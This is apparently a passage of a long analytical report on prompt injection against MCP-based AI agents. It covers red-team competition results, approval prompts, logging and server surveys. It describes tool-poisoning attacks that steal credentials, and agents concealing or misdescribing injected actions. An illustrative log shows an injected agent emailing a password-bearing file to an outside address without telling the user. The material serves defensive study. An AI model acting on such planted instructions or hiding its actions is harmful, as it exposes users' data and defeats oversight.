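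Among the Claude models, the share of harmful actions that passed the prompt judge fell as resistance to attack rose, from 41.9% for Haiku 4.5 to 37.1% for Sonnet 4.5 and 23.7% for Opus 4.5. Amazon's models showed the opposite pattern. Nova 2 Lite resisted attacks better than the older Nova 1 Premier, but 37.8% of its harmful actions passed, compared with 33.2% for Nova 1 Premier. Dziemian and colleagues conclude that obeying an injection and hiding it are at least partly separate tendencies.

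Participants also influenced these shares by choosing which attempts to submit for judging. They saw the agent's response before choosing, and they submitted only about a quarter of their attempts. They had little reason to submit an attempt in which the agent performed the harmful action and then disclosed it. If many participants held such attempts back, the true share of harmful actions that stayed hidden would be lower than the reported share.

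These shares aren't comparable with the covert shares from AgentDojo, because the two studies define concealment differently. Lee and colleagues check whether the answer reveals the injected task. Under the competition's criterion, an attack is concealed if the agent shows no awareness that the instruction was malicious. Some scenarios also required the agent to justify the harmful action to the user. In one, it had to describe a destructive command as routine maintenance recommended by the project's documentation. Lee and colleagues would probably call that success overt because the answer mentions the command, even though the user would be misled about why the agent ran it. Even an honest warning wouldn't prove that the user was safe, because some models point out an attack and still comply with it.

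### What the competition's rates can and can't tell us

The attackers had advantages they would rarely have in practice. They saw the whole conversation up to the point of attack, knew which action they had to cause, and could see which tools the agent had used. The organisers also asked vendors to turn off separate filters that might have caught the attacks. Dziemian and colleagues therefore describe the rates as an upper bound on how vulnerable the models are in a single turn, not as an estimate of how often real attacks work.

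Calling these rates an "upper bound" needs some care, because they average in all participants' failed attempts, including those of beginners, while a persistent attacker needs only one attempt to work. Participants found at least one successful attack on Claude Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios used in the main rounds, and on Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. Successful attacks continued at a roughly constant rate throughout the competition.

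Skilled attackers could also reuse attacks that worked. When the researchers replayed 2,679 successful attacks against every model, those that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked on each of the other models 44–81% of the time. One family of nearly identical attacks worked across 21 scenarios and nine models. But an attack that had worked once often failed when the researchers repeated it on the same model, so one success in the competition doesn't show that an attack is reliable.

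CAISI contributed to the methods of analysis. Its own account, *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, emphasises the sharp differences between models and how attacks carried over from strong models to weaker ones. It treats the results as evidence about hijacked agents in general and doesn't discuss concealment.

Gray Swan has since run new rounds with new scenarios. Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 5 (the safety report published with the model) covers the first quarter of 2026, with 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks that had worked well across models. A single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time against Opus 5 and 3.1% of the time against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic's later card for Claude Fable 5.1 combines two quarters, with 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks. The success rate against Fable 5.1 was 0.1% for one attempt and 1.0% within fifteen attempts,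 compared with 24–53% within fifteen attempts for most models from other developers. In tool use, the rate for Fable 5.1 was 0.0%.

These results show that at least some models have become much more resistant to attack. Neither card gives a separate rate for concealed attacks, so the cards don't show whether the agent's answer is now more likely to reveal an attack that succeeds.

### Whether a visible tool history solves the problem

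Many hosts keep a list of tool calls that the user can open, and it would show the unwanted bank payment even if the final answer didn't mention it. Lee and colleagues assume that the user sees nothing before the final answer, which is too strict for such hosts. They acknowledge that their results may not apply to agents that show users their reasoning.

Dziemian and colleagues reply that most agent interfaces do show a history, but that the logs, like the model's written reasoning, are too long and complicated for people to inspect in practice. This is plausible for a coding agent that has worked for an hour, but they didn't test it on users, and it doesn't fit short sessions. The four covert runs that Lee and colleagues print contain between two and seven tool calls each. The banking run has two, a lookup and a payment. A user who opened the log and saw the names and arguments of the calls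 would probably spot the payment at once.

Other attacks would be hard to spot even in a short list. In one of the covert runs, a user asked for a summary of an article that a colleague had posted. The agent fetched the article and then, on the attacker's instruction, a page whose address differed by one added word. In the history, this looks like an agent reading two pages of the same site. In the competition's email scenario, the history would show an email assistant marking a message as read, and might identify the message only by a number. To recognise either call as harmful, the user would have to know what the agent should have done instead.

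A history therefore helps most when the harmful action is clearly unrelated to the task, and the competition's organisers deliberately avoided such actions. Even then, the user has to expand the history to see the action. An operator may have a fuller record of the session, but the agent has already sent the money by the time anyone reads either record.

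## What approval prompts show and whether people notice

An approval prompt is the dialog a host shows to get the user's permission for a tool call. Unlike a tool history, it appears before the agent acts, so a user who asked for a spending total and then sees a request to pay a stranger can refuse. This works only if the host shows a prompt and the user notices what is wrong with the call.

### What a prompt leaves out

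A typical prompt names the tool and lists the arguments the model filled in, but it doesn't show the text that led the model to propose the call. If the planted comment on issue 214 gets the agent to email a project file to an outside address, the prompt shows an email tool, an address and an attachment. A user who only asked who is working on the issue can see that an email makes no sense, but can't see that the instruction came from the thirty-first comment. If the user had asked the agent to send the file to a contractor, the same prompt would look reasonable, and only someone who knew the contractor's address would notice that the address was wrong.

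The earlier prompt, for the call that fetched the issue, would not have helped, because it appears before the response exists and can show only a request to read issue 214.

Prompts also show a command or call without its effects. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) surveyed approval designs and found that most prompts in production show a raw command on a single line. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), an analysis of 290 reports of agents' mishaps with files, gives the example of a routine-looking command that runs a Python setup script. Approving it permits whatever the script contains. MCP tools have the same problem, because the user sees the arguments but the server's code determines what the call does.

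Refusing a call doesn't remove the planted text from the context either. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, points out that agents are designed to look for another route after a refusal. A user who refuses the email might next see a request to upload the file somewhere, and would have to recognise the new request as part of the same attack.

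### Stolen data beyond the edge of the dialog

An approval prompt can contain the evidence of an attack without the user seeing it. Huang, Huang and colleagues (2026) demonstrated this in *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection*, using a version of Invariant Labs' adding tool. Like the original, it gets the model to copy the user's MCP settings file and SSH credentials into a side note. When the user asks for the sum of 12 and 12, the prompt lists both numbers and the side note, but the visible part looks like an ordinary sum. The user would have to scroll sideways to see the stolen text.

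Huang and colleagues describe this fault in Claude Desktop and Cline, a coding assistant that runs inside Visual Studio Code. Both display every argument, but users must scroll sideways to read long ones. In the tests, the models in both hosts refused to read the files, so the researchers did not learn whether a user would have scrolled far enough. Wrapping long values would fix the layout, but the user would still have to read them and question why adding numbers requires a settings file.

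### Seven hosts and four attacks

This was one of four attacks that Huang and colleagues tried on seven hosts in November 2025. All four used poisoned tool descriptions, so the results don't show how the hosts handle hostile tool responses. The second attack was meant to record the user's requests and tool calls, using a tool described as having priority over all others. The third was meant to make the model write a link with harmless wording and a hostile address, and the fourth to make it download and run a script.

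The researchers rated a result "safe" if something prevented the attack, "partial" if the attack ran with warnings or limits, and "unsafe" if it finished undetected. They also assessed how fully each host displayed a call's arguments, whether it warned of risky operations, and whether it kept a log that users could read.

| Host | File theft | Activity recording | Phishing link | Remote script | Argument visibility | Warnings | Logging |
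|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Desktop | Safe | Partial | Safe | Safe | Partial | Yes | Partial |
| Cursor | Unsafe | Unsafe | Unsafe | Unsafe | Low | No | No |
| Cline | Safe | Safe | Safe | Unsafe | High | Yes | Yes |
| Continue | Safe | Safe | Partial | Safe | Partial | Partial | Partial |
| Gemini CLI | Partial | Safe | Safe | Safe | Partial | Partial | Unknown |
| Claude Code | Partial | Safe | Safe | Safe | Partial | Partial | Unknown |
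| Langflow | Partial | Partial | Safe | Partial | Low | Partial | No |

Of the 28 results, 16 were safe, 7 partial and 5 unsafe. Cursor failed all four attacks, and Cline was the only host rated high for visibility. That rating is doubtful because the paper defines visibility as "partial" when a dialog needs sideways scrolling, and elsewhere it says Cline's dialog does.

*Are AI-assisted Development Tools Immune to Prompt Injection?* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) presents the same test results alongside a review of earlier vulnerability reports. Cline had the highest risk rating of the seven hosts in the review but was one of the two most secure in the tests, so a host's ranking depends heavily on the evidence used.

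In most cases rated "safe", the model refused before any person had to decide, so the rating doesn't show whether a user would have noticed the attack. Gemini CLI and Claude Code passed the phishing test because, in the researchers' view, a terminal can't produce a link that hides its address. Cursor and Cline failed the script test by running a script "when explicitly instructed". If the tester gave that instruction, the result is weaker evidence of injection. Cursor also ran on its own default models while most of the others ran on Claude Sonnet 4.5, so the model may explain part of its poor result.

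These hosts have changed since the study, which tested version 2.0.25 of Claude Code. In July 2026 the testing company Trajectory Labs, commissioned by Anthropic, ran 72 scenarios with planted instructions on version 2.1.205, using MCP tools that control a browser. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that 0.09% of attacks succeeded on average against the company's latest models, even with permission prompts turned off. That is good evidence about the models, but it doesn't show whether the dialogs have improved.

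Yao, Yang and colleagues examined more recent defaults in *When Neither Side Confirms* (November 2026). They found that Continue and Gemini CLI now prompt before every ordinary MCP call. Cline, the host with the best visibility rating a year earlier, now runs these calls by default without prompting.

### Hosts and servers that never ask

Cline is not unusual. For *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications*, Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi (2026) collected 1,723 MCP applications with at least ten GitHub stars. They examined 50 by hand to define the categories, then used a language model to classify the rest from their source code. They checked 30 of the results and found that 96.5% of the labels were correct.

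Only 37.2% of the applications could hold a tool call until the user approved it, while 77.2% had an allow-list, which lets the user decide in advance which servers or tools the model may use. Logging was available in 90.8%, but it doesn't block tool calls. One in five applications had neither an approval step nor an allow-list.

An allow-list, like vetting, does little against a comment planted in a trusted issue tracker, because the user has already enabled the tracker and probably the tools the attacker wants the agent to misuse.

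Majeed and colleagues counted an approval step if they found one in the code. Yao and colleagues instead examined what happens by default, and focused on destructive tools, which can irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands. MCP offers two ways to involve a person before such a tool runs. The host can show its own prompt, or the server can use elicitation, which means sending a question for the host to put to the user.

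To study the server side, the researchers sampled 1,000 code repositories from the official MCP registry. Language models classified a sample of the tools, and two people checked 60 of the classifications. The researchers estimate that 90% of destructive tools have no confirmation step on the server (95% confidence interval 82–95%). Most of the rest accept a confirmation flag that the model can set without anyone's approval.

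AI coding agents traced what 41 popular open-source hosts and frameworks do with an ordinary MCP call in a fresh installation. Seven prompt the user. Codex CLI decides whether to prompt based on the labels that servers put on their tools, and Qwen Code leaves the decision to a classifier. The other 32, made up of 16 of the 25 applications and all 16 frameworks, have no approval step by default.

The researchers then paired each destructive tool in their sample with each of the 25 applications. In 60.7% of pairs, the tool would run without human approval. The figure fell to 47.5% when they added seven closed-source applications, including Claude Desktop and Cursor, whose behaviour they took from documentation. Both percentages weight every application equally, regardless of how many people use it, so they don't measure the share of real tool calls that run without approval.

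Part of the problem is that server and host developers each expect the other's software to ask the user for approval. The developers of one server for the mapping program QGIS turned off its confirmations by default because they expect hosts to prompt. In the sample, 168 tools use elicitation by default, meaning the server asks the user a question through the host. Of these, 130 would still run if the host couldn't relay the question.

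Yao and colleagues also ran some of this software. Crush and Codex CLI showed a dialog, and cancelling it stopped the call. The researchers then tested four frameworks that have no approval step by default. They planted an instruction in a tool's response that told the model to delete an extra note. When the server had no confirmation step, all 180 attempted deletions succeeded. When the server required a confirmation flag that the planted text didn't mention, the models set the flag themselves and deleted the note in 127 of 169 attempts.

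Hosts could close most of this gap by prompting for every tool that the server hasn't labelled as read-only or non-destructive. This would cut the unapproved share from 60.7% to 5.4%. But hosts would also prompt for 82.6% of the tools that looked destructive and turned out not to be, up from 32.5%. Users would see many more prompts, a large part of them for harmless calls.

### What people notice when they choose a server

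Before any of these prompts appear, the user has to choose which servers to install. In *Beyond the Protocol*, Song, Shen and colleagues (2025) studied this choice with 20 participants, most of whom worked or studied in software, AI or security. They built a mock directory of 13 MCP servers, four of them malicious. They first asked participants to choose servers for a travel-planning agent, without mentioning any danger.

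Fifteen of the 20 participants chose at least one malicious server. They picked 3.15 servers on average, and someone picking three at random would include a malicious one 71% of the time, so the participants did about as well as chance. This isn't surprising, since nobody had asked them to look for threats. One reported concentrating on what the servers could do.

The researchers then revealed that four of the servers were malicious and asked participants to find them. One person found all four and eight found none. Participants found 1.15 on average, slightly below the 1.23 expected from naming four servers at random, though some may have named fewer than four. Fourteen people looked mainly at the source code, checking for file operations, outside connections and deliberately confusing code. These checks suit ordinary malware, but they can miss an instruction written in plain English in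 a tool description. Nineteen of the 20 participants said they had little confidence in their answers.

This experiment tested how participants chose servers, so its evidence on approval prompts comes from the interviews afterwards. Nine participants said they had stopped examining dialogs closely after their first few uses, and five routinely turned on automatic approval in hosts such as Cursor and Cline. Even the one person who had found all four malicious servers, a developer with a security background and more than five years' experience, admitted to checking the first couple of prompts and then approving everything.

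### How often people approve

This loss of attention is called approval fatigue. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), a study of developers who use coding agents, cites earlier research on other kinds of software that found people pay less attention to a warning each time it is repeated.

The most widely repeated figures on automatic approval come from Anthropic, which first published them in February 2026. They describe Claude Code, not MCP hosts in general. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* reports that new users fully auto-approve about 20% of their sessions, and that the share passes 40% after roughly 750 sessions. Because these are shares of sessions, they don't mean that 40% of experienced users have turned off their prompts for good.

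The rise may have causes other than carelessness. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), reposted by the blog The Greek Courier, points out that Claude Code asks about every action by default, so some of the increase may come from users adjusting the program to their preferences. Experienced users also interrupted the agent more often than new ones, so some of them may have moved from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in when something looks wrong. Watching can catch an agent that goes off course over several minutes, but a single call that sends out a password finishes before anyone can interrupt it.

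Users approve nearly all of the permission prompts Claude Code shows them. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* put the approval rate at 93% in March 2026, and the company's August article put it at 97%. In August, 25% of interactive sessions started in a mode that skips these prompts.

A high approval rate doesn't by itself show that people aren't reading, because most commands an agent proposes are harmless. Anthropic argues that the high rate does reflect habit, partly because users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents but only 3% of individual permission requests. The comparison is suggestive, but people reject plans for many reasons unrelated to danger, such as wanting a different design.

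The same article reports a controlled experiment that gives better evidence. Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research company for what they thought was a coding study. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only the displayed text changed, so approving it did no harm. Just 143 testers (13.6%) refused. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

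Anthropic had a stake in this result, because it was about to replace most of the prompts with an automated check. The testers were also working in a practice environment, where a destroyed file would not have harmed them, and they might have been more careful with their own projects. But they knew they were being evaluated, and the command was clearly dangerous, while an injected MCP call can look much more ordinary. The exact figure may not apply to MCP dialogs, but it would have to be wrong by a large factor before operators could rely on users to catch most attacks.

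In the analysis of 290 reports of agents' real-world trouble with files, problems with user review contributed to 105 cases. The user had turned on automatic approval in 80 of these, and the prompt gave too little information to judge the action in 31; some cases fall into both groups. These reports can't show how often review prevents damage, since people rarely write about a command they refused.

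### Prompts whose wording an attacker can influence

Even a careful reader can approve the wrong action if the prompt misdescribes it. Some systems let the agent write the explanation the user reads, and an agent that has obeyed a planted instruction may describe its action falsely. With elicitation, the server supplies the question, so a malicious server can choose its wording.

Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, describe a user who asks an agent to email a report to their boss. The agent prepares the email but adds a blind copy to the attacker. Its description of the email is accurate but omits the extra recipient, so a user who reads only the description cannot detect the theft. If trusted software builds the approval prompt from the actual tool call, both addresses appear.

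The researchers gave both versions to 15 language models acting as automated approvers. All 15 approved the email when given the agent's description, and all 15 refused it when given the prompt built from the call. Across the full set of attacks, the models caught 30% with the agent's description and 98% with the call-based prompt. With the call-based prompt, they also refused 16% of harmless requests that resembled attacks, though the researchers attribute most of those refusals to placeholder text in their test material. No people took part, so the experiment shows how much the information matters to an attentive reader but doesn't measure how many users would be attentive.

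An approval prompt built from the tool call still has to match what the software runs afterwards. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten systems for running agents and could test this in eight. In four of those, the action could change after the user had approved it.

An attacker can also try to cause fatigue by making the agent send one request after another until the user gives in. The researchers could test this in seven systems, and none of them limited the number of requests within a run. The researchers' own design does set limits, but the attack still succeeded against it 45–60% of the time with a simulated human approver.

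### What human review can still do

The argument for approval prompts is strongest when the harmful action is plainly unrelated to the task and the user has information that the software lacks. For example, the user may be the only one who knows that their boss has no second email address, or that nobody asked for a payment. Cancelling at the prompt also stops the tool call even if no detector has flagged the injection.

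The argument is much weaker for prompts that appear dozens of times an hour. In Anthropic's experiment, the automated check (called auto mode) blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands. The testers had refused only 6 of the 116 it missed, so also requiring their approval would have stopped very little more. The danger of these coding commands didn't depend on private knowledge, so human approval might help more in cases like the blind copy.

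According to *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), Michael and Roesner analysed 21 proposed designs and five commercial agents and found that current systems often make users choose between repeated approval and automated review that they can't inspect. Since 14 August 2026, new Claude Code sessions on most individual and team plans have used auto mode, in which actions are reviewed automatically, unless the user or an administrator has chosen otherwise. Claude Code returns to manual approval after the automated check has blocked three actions in a row or twenty in a session. Anthropic still recommends that users review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

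## What operators can see in logs and network traffic

If a user approves a harmful call, or the host never asks, the operator may still find the call in a log afterwards. Working out why it happened is harder, because many MCP implementations keep no log or record only minimal operational details, according to the US National Security Agency's security guidance, *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026). The guidance doesn't say how many. Majeed and colleagues found that most MCP applications have some form of logging. However, a log can leave out the tool responses.

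### The records an operator may hold

A tool call passes through several programs, and each can keep its own record. One of them may be a gateway, which sits between hosts and servers and carries an organisation's MCP traffic. The table shows what each record usually holds.

| Record | Tool response | Tool call | Main limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| Host log or transcript | In full, if the host keeps a transcript | Name and arguments | Often stays on the user's machine |
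| Framework trace | Only if the operator turns on content capture | Name and time; arguments only with content capture | Covers only agents whose developers set up tracing |
| Gateway log | In full, if the gateway stores whole messages | The name, or everything if it stores whole messages | Misses servers that the host reaches directly |
| Server log | Depends on the server's developer | Depends on the server's developer | The log of a remote server belongs to its owner |
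| Network record | Not if the connection is encrypted | Not if the connection is encrypted | Shows only the destination, time and amount of data |

A gateway that stores whole messages keeps both the `content` and the `structuredContent` of a response, but many hosts pass only one of them to the model. An investigator could therefore find an instruction in the gateway's log that never reached the model. The host's record is better evidence of what the model read if it stores the text as the host sent it.

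The services the agent uses also keep logs. An operator can usually see in an email provider's logs when a message was sent and to whom. The logs will probably list the user's account as the sender, because the agent works with the user's credentials.

### What OpenTelemetry leaves out by default

Many monitoring products use OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording what software does. It records each piece of work, such as answering a user's question, as a trace. A trace consists of spans, each describing one step, such as a call to a model or a tool. A span's attributes hold the details of that step.

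OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` for what the model sent to a tool and `gen_ai.tool.call.result` for what the tool returned. Both attributes are "Opt-In", so monitoring software omits them unless the operator turns them on, and both come with a warning that they may contain sensitive information. By default, the span has the tool's name and, where available, an identifier for the call. The four MCP-specific attributes listed in OpenTelemetry's *MCP* add no content either. They are the method (such as `tools/call`), the protocol version, the address of a resource and the session identifier.

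Another opt-in attribute, `gen_ai.input.messages`, holds the conversation history that the software sends to the model, including tool responses, so it comes closest to showing what the model received. Error messages can also carry instructions, and this attribute can hold the error text of a failed call, while `gen_ai.tool.call.result` covers only successful calls. But monitoring software may shorten long messages, and it could easily cut an instruction in the thirty-first of forty comments.

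OpenTelemetry leaves content out because it is sensitive and often large. Storing it can be expensive and may conflict with regulations, and operators often want to give fewer people access to users' data than to performance records.

The NSA advises operators to log every tool and model call with the exact parameters, the identities involved and, where feasible, a cryptographic hash of the result. OpenTelemetry's default settings fall short of this advice because they omit the arguments.

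Default traces are also more likely to preserve poisoned tool descriptions than poisoned responses. OpenTelemetry recommends recording the description of each tool the agent calls, if available, so a default trace may include a malicious description. It would not include the one in Trail of Bits' example, because the malicious tool was never called. The full list of tool definitions is a separate opt-in attribute, which OpenTelemetry recommends leaving out by default because of its size.

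Even the default spans require setup. Kludex (2026), a contributor to MCP's Python software kit, proposed built-in tracing that records nothing until a developer connects it to a monitoring system. The conventions were still under development in May 2026, with no public date for a stable version, according to Greptime's *How OpenTelemetry Traces LLM Calls, Agent Reasoning, and MCP Tools* (2026). Existing products keep using older attribute names unless someone switches them, so an operator with several products may have to search for the same information under different names.

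### One compromised session, logged two ways

Suppose the coding assistant can also read files and send email. The user asks who is working on issue 214. A planted comment contains an instruction to email a configuration file to an outside address, and the assistant does so before answering the question.

With content capture on, the trace might contain the lines below. They simplify the records in OpenTelemetry's *LLM call examples* and use invented values. Descriptions in square brackets replace the attacker's text and the file's contents.

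```text
10:02:11  chat                      input_tokens=2150  output_tokens=31
            request="Who is working on issue 214?"
10:02:12  execute_tool read_issue   call_id=c1
            arguments={"number": 214}
            result="Issue 214 ... Assignee: Priya ...
              [comment 31, from a visitor: an instruction to email
              config/export.json to files@outside.example] ..."
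10:02:14  chat                      input_tokens=6480  output_tokens=58
10:02:15  execute_tool read_file    call_id=c2
            arguments={"path": "config/export.json"}
            result="[file contents, including a database password]"
10:02:16  chat                      input_tokens=7438  output_tokens=64
10:02:17  execute_tool send_email   call_id=c3
            arguments={"to": "files@outside.example",
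                       "attachment": "config/export.json"}
            result="Sent"
10:02:18  chat                      input_tokens=7514  output_tokens=9
            answer="Priya is working on issue 214."
```

An investigator can see which file was emailed, where it went, and that the final answer didn't mention the email. The outside address appears in the comment and in the email call but not in the user's request, which is strong evidence that the comment caused the email. The investigator also knows that someone must change the database password, and can search other traces for the same address to find more victims.

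With OpenTelemetry's default settings, the same session leaves this:

```text
10:02:11  chat                      input_tokens=2150  output_tokens=31
10:02:12  execute_tool read_issue   call_id=c1
10:02:14  chat                      input_tokens=6480  output_tokens=58
10:02:15  execute_tool read_file    call_id=c2
10:02:16  chat                      input_tokens=7438  output_tokens=64
10:02:17  execute_tool send_email   call_id=c3
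10:02:18  chat                      input_tokens=7514  output_tokens=9
```

The investigator knows only that the agent read an issue, read a file and sent an email, all without errors. The model's input grew by 4,330 tokens after the first tool call, so the tracker must have returned a long response. The trace doesn't contain the issue number, the file name or the recipient. It would look the same if the user had asked the agent to read the issue and email a file to a colleague, so it gives little reason to investigate.

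Other records can fill some of the gaps. The email provider may have the recipient and the attachment, and the tracker's access log may have the issue number. The investigator could then open issue 214 and find the comment, unless the attacker has edited or deleted it.

A log that follows the NSA's advice falls between these two. It contains the arguments, so the investigator knows the issue, the file and the address, but it may hold only a hash of each result. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from a text. The same text always produces the same hash, but nobody can reconstruct a long text from it. If the investigator fetches the issue again and the hashes match, they have the exact response the agent read. One new comment changes the hash even if the planted comment is still there, so a hash can help check a saved copy of the response but can't replace one.

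### Linking a call to the text that caused it

Ordinary access logs record who did something and whether they had permission, and both can look normal after an injection. The NSA illustrates this risk with the GitHub MCP server, which users give blanket access to act on their behalf in public and private repositories. If an injected agent copies a private file into a public repository, it makes permitted calls with a valid credential, and GitHub's own records may attribute them to the user.

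A full trace adds the order of events, but it doesn't show which input caused the model to send the email. Before sending it, the model had read the system prompt, the tool descriptions, the user's question, forty comments and a file. In the example, the connection is fairly clear because the email went to the address given in the comment. It would be less clear if the comment had sent the agent to a web page for the address, because the instruction and the address would then be in different responses. An attack that makes the agent omit something, such as an urgent email from a summary, may leave no suspicious tool-call argument to match.

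An investigator who has the complete context could test whether the comment led to the action by running the model several times with the comment and several times without it, because output can vary between runs. This requires the same model version. OpenTelemetry recommends recording the exact version that responded, but the vendor may have withdrawn it by the time of the investigation. The NSA's guidance recommends a traceable sequence of actions but gives no method for linking an action to the text that prompted it.

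The text may also have reached the host before the session began. Under the July 2026 specification, a host can reuse a server's tool list for as long as the caching hint allows. A poisoned description could therefore influence a session whose trace contains no `tools/list` request. To check for this later, the operator would need a saved copy of every version of the list.

### Keeping content without creating a second leak

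In the example, the fuller log contains the database password from the stolen file, so anyone who can read the log can read the password. Leaving responses out of the log would not always prevent this. In Invariant Labs' attack with the adding tool, the stolen SSH key was in an argument, so a log that followed the NSA's advice to record exact parameters would have contained the key too.

OpenTelemetry gives operators three options for recording content. They can record none, which is the default. They can put it on the spans, which suits test systems and other settings where the volume is manageable and the storage meets any privacy rules. Or they can store it elsewhere and put only a reference on the span, which OpenTelemetry recommends for production systems with large volumes or sensitive data. Separate storage lets a security team open the content of a suspicious session while developers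 who monitor performance see only the timings. Greptime, a database vendor, reports that most production teams settle on this arrangement, but gives no figures.

Separate storage can also help with sampling. Operators often keep only a fraction of their traces to save money, and a single compromised session among thousands would probably not be in the sample. OpenTelemetry recommends running the step that uploads content for every call, even if the trace is not sampled. That step can also edit the content before uploading it. Removing passwords would leave most planted instructions readable, but cutting long responses to save space might remove the text an investigator needs.

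Stored payloads can also reach another model, because people increasingly use agents to search their logs. The monitoring company Honeycomb reported in the announcement of MCP's July specification that agents make nearly 20% of the interactive queries on its service each month. An agent investigating a compromised session would also read the attacker's comment, and it would have access to the operator's monitoring data.

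### Servers outside the operator's view

An employee can install an MCP server without telling anyone. Many local servers use stdio, where the host starts the server as a program on the same machine and exchanges messages with it directly. These messages never cross the network, so gateways and network monitors can't record them. The operator may see the server connect to an issue tracker, but that traffic looks much like the employee visiting the tracker in a browser.

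The NSA recommends keeping an inventory of all MCP agents and tools and regularly scanning the network for unauthorised servers. Servers can change ports (the numbered entry points for network connections), so it also suggests comparing each scan with earlier ones. A stdio server has no port, so a network scan can't find it. A web-connected server on the user's own machine should accept connections only from that machine, according to Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026), the part of the specification that covers such servers. A network scan will therefore miss many local servers that follow the specification and find the ones that are open to other machines. Operators have to look for the rest on employees' computers, for example in the settings files where hosts list their servers.

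Remote servers are easier to find than local ones but harder to inspect. The operator can record the messages it exchanges with a remote server, but not what happens inside the server. If a remote search tool returns a planted instruction, the operator may not be able to tell whether the server's owner wrote it or the server copied it from a web page. Repeating the search may not help, because the server can return something different. A response can include the server's name and version, but the server supplies both, so they may be inaccurate.

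Tracing can extend into a remote server if the server's owner cooperates. Model Context Protocol documents how a client can pass a trace identifier to the server in a request's `_meta` field. If both sides record their spans under that identifier and share them, the server's steps appear beneath the host's call in one trace. Documentation from Langfuse, a monitoring company, describes separate traces as useful when different teams manage the client and the server. An outside vendor may have customer data to protect and little reason to share its spans, and a malicious server could supply false ones.

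### What the July 2026 specification changes for network tools

Under earlier versions of MCP, the name of a tool appeared only in the JSON body of a request. A gateway that wanted to log tool names had to decrypt each message and then parse its body. The new specification requires clients to copy the method and the tool's name into HTTP headers, which are short labelled lines that come before the body:

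```http
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: read_issue
```

A server can also mark individual arguments, such as a region or customer number, to be copied into headers. The Agentic AI Foundation argues that any proxy or policy engine can now read and route such a request without keeping a shared record of the session.

This makes tool calls easier to log, but HTTPS encrypts the headers along with the body. A device that only monitors encrypted traffic can detect the connection but can't read the headers, and a gateway has to decrypt the request to read them. The new headers also describe only requests. In the example, if all three servers were remote, a log of these headers would contain `read_issue`, `read_file` and `send_email`, much like the default trace, but nothing from the planted comment.

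Before the release, the security company Akamai warned that a request could get past security controls if its headers and body didn't match, according to SC Media's *Model Context Protocol overhaul introduces new security challenges for developers* (2026). For example, a gateway could allow and log a call to one tool while the server ran another. The final specification requires servers that read the body to reject such requests. Older servers may not check for mismatches, so the specification also advises gateways that enforce rules based on these headers to refuse requests that use older protocol versions.

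Headers can also put sensitive data back into logs. The Model Context Protocol proposal for this change advises server developers not to mark passwords, access tokens or personal data for copying into headers, because proxies and logging systems can read them. If a developer ignores this advice, a gateway that logs headers will record that data even when the operator has turned off content capture everywhere else.

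The removal of session identifiers also makes it harder to gather the records of one conversation. When a server issued one, an investigator could use it to find everything from that connection. Now any copy of a server can handle any request, so a conversation's records may be spread over several machines with no session identifier in common. The NSA's guidance, which predates this change, recommends reconstructing the sequence of actions. To do that, operators now need a trace identifier, a conversation identifier from the host or the user's identity on every request. The specification documents how to pass a trace identifier but doesn't require clients to send one.

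Counting requests has become less reliable too. A client now repeats its call when a server requests more information. It must also resend a request, under a new identifier, if the connection breaks before the response arrives. Two `send_email` lines in a gateway log could therefore mean that the model called the tool twice, or that it called it once and the client sent the request twice.

The new specification also deprecates MCP's own logging feature, which servers use to send log messages to clients. In the changelog, Model Context Protocol (2026) recommends that servers use OpenTelemetry instead, or that local servers write to their error output. The old feature will keep working for at least a year. Operators who move to OpenTelemetry will still have to turn on content capture to record what tools return.

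## What real MCP servers and hosts expose

The harm a planted instruction can do depends on which tools the host has connected and what those tools can access. Researchers have surveyed MCP servers to find this out, though nobody knows exactly how many servers exist. The official registry listed 64,935 on 15 November 2026, according to *The Complete Guide to Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025), an online guide with monthly updates. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) collected 67,057 from several registries in June and July 2025. Such lists overstate the number of useful servers, as *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (2025) found when low-value entries inflated the listings of the six marketplaces it examined.

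Four surveys give the most useful evidence about security, and each covers a different group of servers. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) searched the internet for servers that outsiders could reach. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) sent test requests to a smaller group of these reachable servers. *Model Context Protocol (MCP) at First Glance* (Hasan, Li and colleagues, 2025) analysed source code, and *Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025) installed servers and tried their tools.

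| Survey | Sample | Method | Date | Main finding |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Zhou and colleagues | 7,973 remote servers | Internet search, then an MCP handshake | Published May 2026 | 40.55% had no authentication |
| Padilla | 414 remote servers | Live tests of each server | July 2026 | 91.8% lacked OAuth |
| Hasan and colleagues | 583 open-source projects, from 1,899 collected | Code analysis, plus a scan of tool descriptions on 73 servers | Collected March 2025 | 7.2% of the 583 had general vulnerabilities; the scan flagged 5.5% of the 73 for tool poisoning |
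| Zhao and colleagues | 12,230 tools on 1,360 servers | AI classification, human checks and test runs | 2025 | 8.7% of tools had an ability that a data-stealing attack needs |

### Servers that anyone can use

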